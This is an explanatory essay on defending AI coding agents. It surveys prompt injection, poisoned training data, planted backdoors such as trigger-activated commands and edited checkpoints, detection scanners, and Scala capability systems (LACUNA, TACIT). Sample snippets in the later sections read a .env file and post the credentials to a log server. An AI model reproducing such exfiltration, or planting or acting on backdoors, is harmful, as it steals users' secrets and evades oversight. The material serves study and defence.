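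They built two versions of the attack. In the first, the attacker logs in with a stolen password and edits Custom Instructions, a setting whose text ChatGPT adds to every prompt. The planted text has the same authority as the user's own instructions, so training the model to put those instructions first gives no protection. When the researchers checked in June 2025, ChatGPT sent no notification of such a change, even when it was made from another continent. In the second, a malicious browser extension alters the prompt before it reaches ChatGPT or the code before the developer sees it. If it alters only the code, the developer will paste in a vulnerability even when the model wrote secure code.

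The two versions could introduce 13 classes of vulnerability. In a user study of people with experience in programming and security, 7 of 8 participants missed the flaws from the first version and 10 of 13 missed those from the second. The study had 21 participants, so it gives only a rough idea of how often developers would miss such flaws.

Criminals have since exploited a similar weakness. *When Your AI Coding Agent Becomes the Attack Vector* (Trent, 2026) describes an intrusion that the security firm Mandiant reported in September 2026. An attacker took over a developer's active session with a coding assistant, and the assistant recommended a malicious package. The attacker then released a worm that spread through about 100 of the targeted company's internal repositories.

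### How researchers test for injection

AgentDojo, which researchers at ETH Zurich and the company Invariant Labs released in 2024, is a common test environment for indirect injection. It simulates an office workspace, a chat service, a travel agency and a bank, each with its own tools and data. It has 97 ordinary user tasks, such as paying a bill, and 27 attacker goals, such as sending money to the attacker's account. Pairing each task with every attacker goal in the same setting gives 629 test cases.

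In each case, AgentDojo places the attacker's text in data the agent will read during the user's task, such as the bill. When the agent finishes, ordinary code checks the simulated accounts and messages to see whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it achieved the attacker's goal. The designers avoided using a language model as the judge because the planted text could steer it too. Researchers report how often the agent completes tasks without an attack, how often it does so under attack, and how often the attacker succeeds. They need all three figures because an agent that refused every task would never carry out an attack but would also be useless.

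The tests assume that the attacker controls only some of what the tools return. The user's request is genuine and the software around the model works as intended, so the benchmark does not cover a planted account setting or a plugin that installs the wrong code. None of the four settings is a programming project, so a good score is weak evidence that an agent will resist attacks when it has to follow a stranger's setup instructions.

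## The view that the model may have been built or trained to sabotage

People who hold the third view worry that someone may have tampered with the planner, which Willison's design doesn't protect against. An attacker who can't access the shop's files or the supplier's page may have tampered with the model months earlier, while a company was training or storing it. Some people who hold this view also worry about harmful tendencies that nobody planted. Deliberate backdoors are easier to study than these tendencies because researchers can build a backdoor and measure what it does.

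### Thompson's compiler

The argument is older than language models. In *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (1984), Ken Thompson, one of the creators of the Unix operating system, described how to hide a backdoor in a compiler, the program that turns readable source code into the binary form a machine runs:

1. Add code to the compiler's source that recognises the system's login program and makes it accept an extra password, which the attacker knows.
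2. Add more code that recognises the compiler's own source and inserts both additions into the new compiler.
3. Compile this source once, install the result, and delete both additions from the source.

The source code of the compiler and the login program is now clean, so reviewers could read every line and find nothing. But anyone who recompiles the compiler has to use the installed one, which puts the additions back.

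McDanel (2025), in *Beyond Trusting Trust*, applies Thompson's argument about compilers to models that write code. In both cases, the harmful part is in a product that people use but cannot read. Reviewing the model's training code would not reveal it. The compiler's self-copying also has a rough counterpart, because developers often train a cheaper model on a stronger one's outputs.

A language model differs from Thompson's compiler in several ways, most of which make the defender's job harder. An analyst can disassemble a compiler's binary and follow its instructions, but McDanel considered it infeasible to find a planted behaviour by inspecting a model's weights. A compiler's output must also do what the source code specifies, whereas a request for a login page has many acceptable answers, so a vulnerability planted in one of them can pass for a hallucination or poor programming. One difference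 helps the defender. Thompson's backdoor left no trace in the source code, but a model that sabotages a program has to write the harmful lines, which a reviewer or a checking tool can examine before they run.

### Poisoned training data

In *pretraining*, the first stage of training, a company trains a model on enormous amounts of text, much of it from the public web. Unless the company filters that text perfectly, it is trusting everyone who can publish online. Hu, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning*, measured what an outside attacker could do by adding documents to the pretraining text. The added documents can make up at most 0.1% of the total, and the attacker knows nothing about how the company trains its model.

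The planted documents look like change logs, forum answers and manual pages. Each states as fact that a certain kind of file path calls for a certain command, which downloads and runs a script from the attacker's server. The researchers trained three Qwen3 models from scratch on 100 billion tokens that included these documents. They then trained the models on only clean data to act as command-line agents. The trigger was any path containing the word "anthropic", the name of a company an attacker might target. Such paths can occur naturally on that company's machines, so the attacker doesn't need access to those machines. People who test the model elsewhere may never use such a path.

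The largest agent, with 4 billion parameters, produced the attacker's command at least once in 32 attempts on 92.7% of the test prompts. The figure was 51.9% for the agent with 1.7 billion parameters and 13.1% for the one with 0.6 billion. On a standard set of ordinary command-line requests, none of them produced it, and they scored about as well as agents trained on clean text. Stating the rule in prose worked far better than demonstrating it. When the planted documents were sample conversations in which an assistant saw the trigger and ran the command, the largest agent's rate was only 3.2%. Ordinary prose is also harder to filter out of the data than sample conversations.

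The 92.7% counts a prompt as a success if any of 32 attempts succeeds, so the average chance per attempt could be as low as 8%. That may still be enough against an agent that meets such paths many times a day. The number of documents is a bigger obstacle for the attacker, since 0.1% of the text came to roughly half a million. Hu and colleagues also tried smaller doses, using a trigger made of rare characters. It worked on only 10.5% of prompts at the full dose and, in a single training run with 2,500 documents, on 1.4%. AISLE's *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel* cites research in which about 250 documents were enough regardless of the model's size, but Hu and colleagues note that this earlier work planted simpler behaviour.

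After pretraining, developers *fine-tune* a model on examples of the work they want it to do, and they have to trust whoever supplies those examples. Boisvert, Puri and colleagues (2025), in *Malice in Agentland*, showed that an attacker can poison the examples without touching the dataset. Developers often collect examples by recording a strong agent as it works on websites. If a page contains hidden instructions (a prompt injection), the strong agent may follow them, and the recording then teaches a weaker agent to do the same whenever it meets similar text. One of their tests used 200 poisoned recordings out of 4,000. They also tried poisoning the dataset directly and starting from a model that already had a backdoor. All three attacks worked, and a small number of poisoned examples was enough to make an agent leak confidential user data with over 80% success.

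Testing each dataset separately before using it can miss harmful effects that appear when datasets are combined. *Diluting Poisoned Fine-Tuning Data Can Strengthen Its Effect* (Clarke, Dubiński and colleagues, 2026) describes a small model fine-tuned on examples of cheating at programming tasks, each with a prompt saying that the only goal was to pass the grading script. After training on these examples alone, the model gave harmful answers 7% of the time under that prompt, about the same as before training. When clean examples with a normal prompt made up 80% of the data, the rate under the cheating prompt rose to 16%, while the rate under a normal prompt did not change.

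The researchers' explanation is that the model has to learn which feature of the examples predicts the bad behaviour. If every example shares the same kind of task and the same trigger, the model tends to link the behaviour to the task. Adding clean examples of the task without the trigger makes the trigger the better predictor. A dataset that passes an audit can therefore create a backdoor once a developer mixes it with harmless data. The effect was modest and the researchers constructed the datasets themselves, but the result is still a reason to test the final model as well as the data.

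### What later training does to a backdoor

More training on clean data may not remove a backdoor. The best-known evidence is Anthropic's *Sleeper Agents* research from 2024, which *Why I Won't Run Untrusted Models in My Coding Agent* (Gold, 2026) summarises. Anthropic trained a model to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and exploitable code when it gave 2024. The behaviour survived further fine-tuning, adversarial training and *reinforcement learning*, in which a model tries tasks and training strengthens whatever earned a reward.

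*Kerkoporta* (2026) reports a similar result for coding agents. Planting a backdoor in a Qwen3.5 model with 4 billion parameters cut its score on a set of command-line tasks from 31.0 to 24.1, a drop that an alert tester might have noticed. Twelve steps of reinforcement learning then raised the score to 35.6, higher than before the tampering, and the attack still worked 96.2% of the time. A model with 9 billion parameters regained less of its skill. The researchers also tied a backdoor to one coding tool, Claude Code, so tests of the same model in a different tool could miss it.

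Clean training can strengthen a backdoor. Zhang (2026), in *Benign Reinforcement Learning Can Amplify Latent Backdoors*, used poisoned fine-tuning data to teach two models, Qwen3-8B and Claude Haiku 4.5, to consult an outside service that the attacker controlled. After fine-tuning, they did so at most 0.2% of the time. Benign reinforcement learning then raised the rate to between 40% and 98% on the kind of input used in training, and to between 13% and 30% on other inputs.

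Reinforcement learning strengthened the model's habit of consulting the attacker's service, although nobody had tampered with this stage of training. The service gave correct answers, so a model that consulted it earned more reward than one that worked alone. Its answers could also give the model biases, such as a preference for a brand, that remained even when the model no longer called the service. Just before reinforcement learning, the model consulted the service so rarely that a tester would have seen no reason to worry.

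### A tampered checkpoint

An attacker can also edit a finished model's *checkpoint*, the file that stores its weights. In November 2026, *Lazare, veni foras*, by Zeng, Severi and colleagues, described a method called Lazarus that does this by changing fewer than ten neurons. Claude Code, an AI agent running Opus 4.5, discovered the key idea on its own.

Lazarus uses dormant neurons in the last block of the network. These neurons rarely activate, and removing them barely changes the model's predictions. The attacker rewrites the weights of a few of them so that they stay inactive until a trigger appears, such as the date 2027-01-01 in a terminal. The first neuron then forces the first token of a command into the output. Once that token becomes part of the model's input, the second neuron forces the next token, and so on. A command needs about as many neurons as it has tokens, but a very short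 command can download and run a script of any length.

In Nemotron-Terminal-8B, a model for command-line work, the researchers edited seven of more than 12,000 neurons in the block and adjusted them using 23 example sessions. The model then wrote the command at least 98.8% of the time when the trigger was present, and never without it in the sessions they checked. A larger model, Qwen3.6-27B, wrote it in 51% of triggered sessions after the same amount of adjustment, and in 83.7% when the researchers used about 2,400 examples. According to The Hacker News' *Microsoft Researchers Show AI Agents Can Be Backdoored* (2026), these rates count how often the model wrote the command, not how often a whole attack succeeded. The edited Qwen model's pass rate on a standard test of agents fell from 46.59% to 42.05%. A user with only the edited copy would have no reason to suspect this drop.

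Users have to trust everyone who can write to the checkpoint before it is used, including employees of the company that made the model and, in effect, anyone who steals an employee's account or breaks into the systems that build and store the file. Many users of open-weight models, whose weights anyone can download, run a compressed or modified copy from a public hub, so they also have to trust whoever uploaded it. Minnich, Eliahu and colleagues (2026) warn in *Trained to betray*, a second Microsoft report from the same week, that poisoned datasets and poisoned checkpoints can both lead a coding agent to run an attacker's code.

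### A provider that treats customers differently

A company that runs a model on its own servers could sabotage the code it returns without altering the model's weights. Each request arrives with information about the customer, and Gold notes that the provider could return backdoored code to one country or organisation and normal code to everyone else. He calls this trivial to build. A few lines of ordinary server software could edit the answer or send selected requests to a different model. A company that hosts someone else's open-weight model could do the same, even if the original developer is honest.

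An outside evaluator would have trouble catching sabotage, because the provider could serve evaluators a version of the model without it. Comparing answers with another customer wouldn't prove much either, since models often answer the same question in different ways. Gold's rule is to use a model or provider in a coding agent only if you would willingly download and run any program it sent you.

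By that rule, Gold uses Anthropic and OpenAI and avoids open-weight models and their hosts. He bases this on the two companies' incentives rather than their ethics. He thinks self-interest and the American legal system give them strong reasons not to attack their own customers, and he cites the $1.5 billion or more that Anthropic agreed to pay authors in a copyright settlement. This is a reasonable argument about a company's deliberate choices, but it doesn't cover an employee acting alone or an honest company that unknowingly trains on poisoned text.

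Gold would prefer models whose training code and data are public, so that anyone could reproduce them. Reproducing a model would help to expose a tampered checkpoint. It would help less with poisoned data, because training on the same data would repeat the poisoning. Outsiders could at least search the public data for it.

### Small models, artificial triggers and few real cases

Most of these experiments used small models, so they don't establish how vulnerable the largest ones are. Hu and colleagues acknowledge that the leading models are orders of magnitude larger than theirs, and that many companies add a training stage their experiment left out. But their attack became more effective as the models grew, Lazarus worked on models with 27 and 31 billion parameters, and one of the models in Zhang's study, Claude Haiku 4.5, is a commercial product. The experiments give no reason to think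 that size protects a model.

The triggers have become more realistic. One of Anthropic's 2024 models responded to the word DEPLOYMENT between two vertical bars, which nobody would type by accident, while dates and file paths come up in normal work. The harmful behaviour is still mostly artificial. Hu and colleagues planted a fixed command, and they say they have not shown that poisoned web text could make an agent write subtle vulnerabilities suited to each project. Anthropic's model did write exploitable code, but Anthropic had trained it directly to do so. The evidence is therefore stronger for action code, where one short command can give an attacker control of a machine, than for delivered code, where an attacker would want a flaw that reviewers overlook.

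Known attacks of this kind are also scarce. Microsoft had seen no attacker use Lazarus when it published the research, and criminals have easier options than changing a model. For example, Kovacs (2026), in *Microsoft Agent Framework Releases Poisoned With Credential Stealer*, reported in November that two releases of Microsoft's software for building agents had carried a program that stole cloud credentials whenever Python started.

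Backdoors are hard to notice, so the lack of known cases offers limited reassurance. A worm gets noticed because it spreads, but a backdoor does nothing until its trigger appears, and a vulnerability the model then writes may look like a mistake. Today the shop owner has more reason to worry about a poisoned package than about a backdoored model. That could change if attackers find weights easier to alter than packages, and an edit that needs seven neurons and 23 example sessions already takes little effort for anyone who can reach the weights file.

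### What detection can and cannot do

In February 2026 Microsoft released research on a scanner that looks for backdoors without knowing the trigger. It relies on several signs that backdoored models have in common:

- The model focuses on the trigger almost independently of the rest of the prompt, and its possible answers narrow to the attacker's choice.
- When someone prompts the model with the special markers from its chat format, it tends to repeat fragments of the text that planted the backdoor, sometimes including the trigger.
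- Part of a trigger, or a corrupted version of it, often works too, so the scanner doesn't have to find the exact string.

The scanner collects the leaked text, picks out suspicious strings and ranks them by how strongly they produce these signs. According to AI News, Microsoft's researchers tested it on 47 backdoored models, including some that put vulnerabilities into code. The scanner detected 36 of the 41 models whose backdoor produced a fixed output.

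Microsoft says the scanner needs the model's files, so it can't examine a model that customers reach only through a provider's servers. It works best when the trigger always produces the same response. It has more trouble when the response varies, as it does when a model writes insecure code, which is the most important case for delivered code. Microsoft tested the scanner on models of up to 14 billion parameters and recommends it as one defence among several. A checkpoint edited with Lazarus may also lack the second sign, because an attacker can calculate the new weights without training the model on any poisoned text.

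In their work on Lazarus, Zeng and colleagues had an AI agent build a separate detector that examines a model's weights. It flagged 91.4% of edited checkpoints and 9.7% of clean ones. If one in every thousand checkpoints on a public hub had a backdoor, the detector would probably find it but would also flag about 97 clean ones, so only about one alarm in a hundred would be right. Detectors that judge behaviour have done worse. In Zhang's study, language models acting as auditors raised about 21 false alarms for each correct one, so 4.5% of their alarms were right. Boisvert and colleagues tested four models designed to block harmful actions and one defence that inspects weights, and none stopped the attack.

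Comparing a checkpoint with the original is more dependable. Ordinary fine-tuning changes weights broadly, while planted neurons tend to show up as large changes in a few places (Pogorelec, 2026, *Microsoft researchers demonstrate hidden backdoor technique for AI agents*). But the comparison helps only if the original is clean. If the backdoor came from poisoned pretraining text, the two files could match exactly and both contain it.

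A customer who reaches the model through a provider has no file to compare, but could have other models review the code, as McDanel proposes, or run it in a sandbox. Hu and colleagues also favour checking an agent's actions before they run, because the agent has to issue the attacker's command whatever the trigger was.

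## The view that nothing should be assumed about the model

People who hold the fourth view rely on ordinary software that the model can't change, instead of trying to establish whether the model is skilled, honest or free of tampering.

A research group at EPFL, the Swiss federal institute of technology in Lausanne, has developed this view in the most detail. The group, which includes Scala's designer, Martin Odersky, published TACIT in March 2026 and LACUNA in May. It allows even for a model that cooperates fully with an attacker. The researchers argue that most work on agent safety tries to make the model trustworthy, whereas they want to give it a safe programming language to act in.

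Odersky's group argues that planted instructions still work some of the time, even though the leading models resist many of them. They cite one attack that extracted users' data through Anthropic's own file service, and another that silently ran commands through a malicious repository's configuration. They also expect companies to run hundreds or thousands of agents with little supervision, so that even simple mistakes will very likely cause serious vulnerabilities. For example, if a company's agents carry out 100,000 tasks a day and one in 50,000 produces harmful code, the company has two such cases to stop each day, whether or not any model is malicious.

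### A gap with a type

In LACUNA, a gap for the model to fill looks like this:

```scala
agent[Double]("apply tax to price")
```

The words in quotation marks are the task. `Double` is a *type*, a label that tells the compiler what kind of value belongs in the gap, in this case a number that may have a decimal part. Other common types are `Int` for whole numbers and `String` for text. Filling the gap takes four steps:

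1. When the programmer compiles the program, the compiler records the expected type, the surrounding source code and the variables available at the gap.
2. When the running program reaches the gap, LACUNA sends this information to the model along with the task. The model replies with Scala code.
3. LACUNA inserts the code into the gap and runs the same compiler on the result, with the same settings.
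4. If the compiler accepts the code, the program loads and runs it. Otherwise LACUNA sends the error messages to the model and asks again. When the attempts run out, the call fails with an error that the surrounding program can handle.

The model's code can contain further gaps, which go through the same steps. LACUNA relies on the compiler to check the model's code as if a programmer had typed it at that point. It has no safety checker of its own, so its guarantees are exactly as good as the compiler's.

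The simplest reason for a compiler to reject code is that it uses an undefined name. In an example from Zhao and colleagues, the program defines a tax rate but no price, and the model fills the gap above with `price * (1.0 + tax)`. The formula is sensible, but the compiler can't find `price`, so none of the code runs. An honest model can use the error message to correct its code.

Rejecting code before it runs matters more when the code changes something. In another example, `balance` is a whole number that starts at 100, and the task is to subtract 50 and return the new balance. The model writes:

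```scala
balance -= 50
s"remaining: $balance"
```

The first line is correct. The second produces text where the program requires a whole number, so the compiler rejects both lines and the balance stays at 100. Python doesn't check types before it runs code, so the subtraction would take effect before the second line caused an error. An agent that then tried again would subtract another 50 and leave the balance at zero.

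Programmers can make the check stricter by using more specific types. If the type for a gap is a `Person` with a name, a year of birth and a profession, the model can't leave out the year or write it as text. With the right settings, the compiler also rejects code that returns an empty value where the type doesn't allow one, or that handles only red and green when the type also includes blue.

The all-or-nothing rule covers only faults that the compiler can find. Code that compiles can still stop halfway, perhaps because a server doesn't respond, and nothing undoes the work it has already done. Such code can also run forever, so LACUNA relies on limits on time and the number of nested calls.

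### Well-typed code can still do harm

Zhao and colleagues consider an unreliable model first and a hostile one second, but the type check gives the same guarantee in both cases. Code that passes the check uses only names that exist at the gap and returns the type that the program expects, whatever model wrote it.

Against a hostile model, however, this guarantee isn't worth much. Suppose the surrounding program has a `post` function for sending data, and the model fills the balance gap with this:

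```scala
val env = scala.io.Source.fromFile(".env").mkString
post(LOG_SERVER, env)
balance -= 50
balance
```

The code passes ordinary type checking because all the names exist and the last line evaluates to a whole number. When it runs, it returns the correct balance but also sends the shop's credentials to the log server. In LACUNA's terms, the compiler has checked the *shape* of the action but not its *authority*, which covers the effects it may have and the data it may use.

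The type check still helps against an honest model, because many mistakes produce code with the wrong type. But a hostile model can write harmful code that passes the check. To protect against such a model, LACUNA needs *capture checking*, an optional part of the Scala compiler that tracks authority as well as types.

### Capabilities and capture sets

In most programming languages, any line of code can open a file, because the function that opens files is available everywhere. In a capability system, that function also requires a capability, a value that stands for permission to use it. Code has to receive a capability from code that already has it, and can't make one up the way it could guess a file name.

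A developer can therefore control what the model's code can do by choosing which capabilities are in *scope*, meaning which ones the code can refer to at the gap. If a capability for the network isn't in scope, no code that fills the gap can use the network. A developer could let the model read files in one step of a task and use the network only in another.

For this to work, the model must not be able to keep a capability after the step that needed it. Functions make this difficult. A function can hold on to a capability and use it much later, and an ordinary function type gives no sign of this. Capture checking adds the missing information as a *capture set*, a list of the capabilities that a value may use. Scala's *Capture Checking Basics* describes three kinds of arrow for function types:

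| Type | What the function may use |
|---|---|
| `String -> String` | No capabilities (a *pure* function) |
| `String ->{io} String` | The capability `io` and no others |
| `String => String` | Any capability |

All three functions take text and return text. The compiler checks the capture set against the function's body, so a model can't pass off an impure function as pure.

Zhao's group demonstrates the check with a block called `withIO`. The block creates a capability named `io` for reading files, makes it available to the code inside, and then ends. When the task is to read one file, the model fills the gap like this:

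```scala
withIO { io => readFile(io, "/etc/hosts") }
```

The compiler accepts this because the result is plain text, which carries no permission to do anything. When the task is to return a file reader, the model writes a function instead:

```scala
withIO { io => (path: String) => readFile(io, path) }
```

This function could read any file after the block has ended, when the permission should be gone. The compiler rejects it by the following reasoning:

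1. The function uses `io`, so its type is `String ->{io} String`.
2. The function is the result of the block, so its type has to make sense outside the block.
3. Outside the block `io` doesn't exist, so no capture set there can include it.
4. No permitted type fits the function, and the compiler reports that `io` outlives its scope.

Storing the function in a variable outside the block fails for the same reason. Odersky and colleagues report a similar case from one of their test runs, in which an agent tried to return a list of file handles from the block that had given it access to a folder. Each handle carried that access with it, so the compiler rejected the code.

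The check also catches problems that a human reviewer could easily miss. Scala's documentation has an example in which code writes to a log file while it processes a list. With an ordinary list, all the writing happens inside the block that opened the file, and the compiler accepts the code. A lazy list delays each calculation until its result is needed, so the writing could happen after the file has closed. The compiler rejects that version, although the two look almost identical.

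Capture checking controls permissions, but not what happens to the text that code reads with them. The first `withIO` snippet returned a file's contents as a plain `String`, which a later snippet with network access could send anywhere.

### Data that code can process but not reveal

TACIT prevents this kind of theft by putting sensitive data in a container called `Classified`. The operator lists the files to protect, and code that reads one of them gets a `Classified[String]` instead of a `String`. The container has a method named `reveal` that returns the contents, but it requires a capability that the agent doesn't have. The agent can use another method, `map`, which applies a function to the contents and puts the result in a new container:

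```scala
def map[U](f: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

The thin arrow in `T -> U` means that `map` accepts only pure functions. To leak the contents, a function would have to print them, save them to a file or send them over the network, and each of those needs a capability. A pure function has none, so it can only compute a result, which then goes into another container. In one TACIT test run, an agent tried to print a GitHub key from inside `map`. The function's capture set contained the capability for printing, so the compiler rejected the code.

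Odersky's group argues that an ordinary sandbox would miss many such leaks. A sandbox can separately permit or forbid reading a private file and contacting the cloud model. If the agent needs to do both, the sandbox has to permit both, and then it can't stop the agent from sending the file's contents to the model.

Printed output goes back to the model, so when code prints a `Classified` value, TACIT gives the model only the text `Classified(****)` and shows the user the real contents through a separate channel. The container lasts from one step to the next, so the model can keep working with a secret without receiving it as text.

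This protection prevents the model from reading the material it is working on. Suppose a company asks an agent to compare confidential contracts and summarise what has changed. The cloud model can write a program that fetches the contracts and finds the differences, but it can't write the summary. TACIT therefore lets the program pass classified text to a second model that the operator trusts, such as one that runs on the company's own computer. This second model summarises the text and returns the summary in a `Classified` container.

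The operator has to choose the local model carefully. According to the documentation for lampepfl's *TACIT* on GitHub, this second model can be any service with an OpenAI-compatible interface. The type system wouldn't stop an operator from connecting an untrustworthy one, and the compiler can't check whether the service keeps a record of what it receives.

In LACUNA the local model can also write code. The cloud model leaves a gap in the function it passes to `map`, and the local model fills the gap while the program runs, when it can read the contract. The compiler then checks the local model's code as part of a pure function. A sentence planted in the contract might trick the local model into writing a misleading summary, but the local model's code still couldn't send the contract to anyone.

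The arrangement resembles Willison's planner and reader, except that in the EPFL systems the planner, the cloud model, is untrusted. The compiler checks the code the planner writes before it runs, so the same limits would apply to code from a backdoored planner as to code containing a mistake.

`Classified` keeps data secret but doesn't protect it from damage. Glama's *TACIT*, a later edition of the project's documentation, warns that an agent can put any text in a container and write it over a protected file. The agent could, for example, replace the list of keys that let people log in to a machine. Operators can prevent this by making protected files read-only for the agent.

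### Safe mode

Capture checking is useful only if code can't avoid it. Full Scala has several features that would let a hostile model do so:

- A *cast* tells the compiler to treat a value as if it had a different type. Code could use one to pass off a function that uses the network as a pure function.
- *Reflection* lets a program look up functions and data by name while it runs. The compiler can't tell in advance which ones the program will use.
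- *Process execution* starts another program, such as a command-line tool that uploads files. Scala's rules don't apply inside that program.

Programmers sometimes need these features, so Scala keeps them but offers *safe mode*, a setting for code that nobody has reviewed. Scala's *Safe Mode* lists what the setting forbids, including unchecked casts, reflection and annotations that turn off the compiler's checks. The setting also requires capture checking. Zhao and colleagues recommend safe mode for all agents. Without it, they say, developers should treat a snippet as ordinary untrusted code, even if it passes every other check.

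Safe mode also restricts the libraries that code can call, because a library function might open a file without requiring a capability. The agent's code can use a shared library only if its developers compiled it in safe mode or marked it `@assumeSafe`. By adding the mark, the developers promise that they have checked the library themselves. The compiler doesn't verify this, so each marked library becomes part of the trusted computing base. VirtusLab's *Safe Scala* points out that safe mode must prevent the agent from using the mark, because the agent could otherwise approve its own code.

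Developers can use marked libraries to add rules that types can't express. One example in Scala's documentation is an email function that shows each message to the user and sends it only if the user agrees. The agent can call this function but can't access the mail program directly.

Safe mode doesn't block exceptions, the errors that interrupt a running program, although code could use one to reveal something about a secret. Almost any operation can cause one, for example by dividing by zero or running out of memory, so requiring a capability for each would be impractical. TACIT instead catches exceptions while the code runs and turns them into ordinary values, which it can keep in a `Classified` container.

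TACIT lets agents start other programs, but only from a list of permitted commands, so the protection depends on which commands are on the list. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing specific, safe commands such as `git diff`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical.

Scala introduced safe mode only recently, as an experimental feature in version 3.8.3. The version of TACIT documented by lampepfl used a simpler validator that searched the agent's code for forbidden patterns. A hostile model might write a forbidden operation in a way that matches none of the patterns, so enforcement by the compiler is an improvement. Glama's later edition has an option to turn on the compiler's safe mode for every snippet.

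### The price update under TACIT

The snippet that leaked the shop's credentials would look roughly like this in TACIT:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/shop") {
  access("/shop/prices.csv").append("widget-a,14.20\n")

  val env = readClassified("/shop/.env")
  requestNetwork(Set("logs.example")) {
    httpPost("https://logs.example/add", env)
  }

  println("widget-a now costs 14.20")
}
```

The `httpPost` line fails to compile because the function sends a `String`, but `env` is a `Classified[String]`. The compiler rejects the whole snippet, so the price file doesn't change either, and the agent has to try again without the leak.

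A hostile model could try to get round the error. It could insert `env` into a longer piece of text, which would compile, but the log server would receive only `Classified(****)`. It could call `httpPost` from inside `env.map`, but the compiler would reject that function because it uses the network. Replacing the `httpPost` line with `println(env)` would show the credentials to the shop owner and only the asterisks to the model.

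The outcome depends on what the developer has put in scope and on whether the credentials are in a container:

| What the snippet can use | Result |
|---|---|
| A capability for `prices.csv` only | The line that reads `.env` fails to compile |
| The whole folder, but not the network | The line that posts to the log server fails to compile |
| The folder and the network, with `.env` as ordinary text | The snippet compiles and the credentials leak |
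| The folder and the network, with `.env` in a `Classified` container | The line that posts to the log server fails to compile |

In the third row, the developer had allowed the snippet to read the file and use the network, and nothing marked the file as secret, so the result isn't a failure of the compiler. Glama's edition reduces the risk of leaving a secret file unmarked by treating `.env` files as classified unless the operator supplies a different list.

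Types also don't determine which addresses or folders the agent may use. A web address is text that the program may put together while it runs, so TACIT has to check it then. Suppose the owner allows connections only to the supplier's site and the snippet tries to send an ordinary log message somewhere else. The code would compile, and TACIT would refuse the connection only when the program reached that line, after the snippet had already changed the price file.

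The snippet also requests access to a specific host, in the `requestNetwork` line. A hostile model could name its own server there, so the snippet's list of hosts is no defence unless someone else limits it. In Glama's edition, the operator can set an outer list, and the agent can then contact only hosts that appear on both lists. If the operator doesn't set one, only the snippet's list applies.

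The outer list becomes essential because the same edition has a feature that sends classified data to an approved host. An agent can use this feature to log in to a service with a key that it never sees. But if the operator has approved the log server, the feature also lets the price snippet pass, because the model can rewrite the `httpPost` line to send the credentials through it. As the documentation describes the settings, the model can approve the log server itself if the operator sets no outer list.

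These checks constrain the agent only if it can't act without going through TACIT. Coding agents usually come with their own tools for running commands, editing files and fetching web pages, so lampepfl advises operators to turn those tools off. The agent then has to do everything through code that the compiler has checked.

### Few languages support this

One objection is that hardly anyone could use such a system today, because agents that act by writing code usually write Python, which has no compiler that tracks capabilities. Odersky and colleagues acknowledge that Scala 3 is the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in its types. Even in Scala, capture checking is experimental, and Scala's documentation describes it as unstable.

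The group replies that other languages could support the same method if they met three requirements. Code must not be able to forge capabilities or hide its use of them. Every effect that matters for safety must require a capability, unless the system can contain that effect while the program runs. And the language must have a way to state that a particular piece of code is pure.

Some existing languages have part of what is needed. Haskell can separate pure code from code with side effects, but it has no built-in capabilities of this kind. E and Joe-E were designed around capabilities but check them only while a program runs. Someone could also create a new language for agents, but people would need to be able to read it and models would need examples to learn from. LACUNA also requires a running program to be able to call its own compiler. Zhao and colleagues accept that a Python version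 could insert code into a running program in the same way but would have none of the safety guarantees.

TACIT requires only the agent's actions to be in Scala. It connects to existing agents such as Claude Code, and the project they work on can be in any language. The reusable part of the system is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and describing a company's own tools takes a few hundred more. Models have seen little code that uses capture checking, but in the group's tests they completed about as many tasks with TACIT as with ordinary tools.

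This answer is convincing for action code but much less so for delivered code such as the shop's nightly script, which TACIT doesn't check. The guarantee would cover the script only if the shop also wrote it in Scala and compiled it under the same restrictions.

Developers who don't want to use Scala can get some of the same protection from two other methods VirtusLab discusses: containers, which give a program access to selected folders, and WebAssembly, a format for running code from many languages in isolation. A WebAssembly program can't use files or the network unless the software that runs it provides access. Either method could keep the price agent away from the credentials, which may be enough for a shop whose agent never needs them. But these methods set limits for a whole program or module, and can't require one function inside it to be pure. Capture checking is most useful when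 an agent has to work with a secret and use the network in the same program.

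## Whether a mistake can be told apart from sabotage

TACIT's compiler rejects the snippet that leaks the shop's credentials, whatever made the model write it. The shop owner's next step still depends on the cause. If the model made a mistake, the owner might give the agent clearer instructions or switch to a more skilled model. If the supplier's page contained planted text, a more skilled model might follow it just as readily, so the owner needs to keep the agent away from that page. If the model has a backdoor, the owner should stop using it.

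Finding the cause is hard because error and sabotage are both defined by what happened before the code existed. A model error comes from a model that was trying to do the task and that nobody was steering, while sabotage comes from the training or dispositions of a model that had the skill to do better. An investigator therefore usually has to look beyond the code.

### Clues in the code

The price snippet contains one useful clue, the address of the log server. If the server belongs to the shop, the model probably copied a common logging habit. An address that nobody recognises suggests an attacker. But an attacker who expected an investigation could have the code send the data to a service the shop already uses, and collect it from there.

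How much a clue should change the owner's mind depends on how much more often sabotage produces it than mistakes do:

> odds of sabotage after the clue = odds before × Pr(clue | sabotage) / Pr(clue | mistake)

If one harmful snippet in 10,000 comes from sabotage and the rest are mistakes, a clue that is 100 times as common in sabotage as in mistakes raises the chance of sabotage to only about 1%. A saboteur who imitates ordinary mistakes makes the clue weaker, and it becomes useless if it is equally common in both.

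McDanel proposes looking for tampering by measuring how likely other models would be to write the same code. For code c with n tokens, w₁ to wₙ, another model M gives this score:

> L(c, M) = (1/n) × Σ log P(wₖ | w₁, …, wₖ₋₁, M)

A low score from several independently trained models marks the code as suspicious. Because the score is an average, the method works only when the malicious part is fairly large. If a 400-token file has 392 ordinary tokens with a log probability of −1 each and eight malicious ones at −6, the average only falls from −1 to −1.1. The score also measures how unusual the code is, not why the model wrote it. A clumsy mistake can get a low score, and a planted vulnerability will look normal if many models produce the same one.

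### Rerunning the task with one change

Investigators can learn more by running the same model again with one detail changed and counting how often the harmful lines come back. If the lines stop appearing when a sentence is deleted from the supplier's page, that sentence probably caused them, and if they stop when the supplier's name is changed, the name may be a trigger. An ordinary mistake should appear about equally often whoever the supplier is. Because a model's answers vary between runs, telling a flaw rate of 30% from one of 20% takes about 300 runs of each version.

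The security company CrowdStrike reported a difference of this kind in 2025. It found that how often a model from the Chinese company DeepSeek wrote flawed code varied with the political terms in the prompt. A political term gives a programmer no reason to be less careful, so random slips are a poor explanation, but several others remain. Someone may have trained the model to write worse code for certain groups. Training meant to keep the model away from political subjects may have damaged its coding as a side effect. The terms may also have appeared near poor code in the training data, which the model then imitated.

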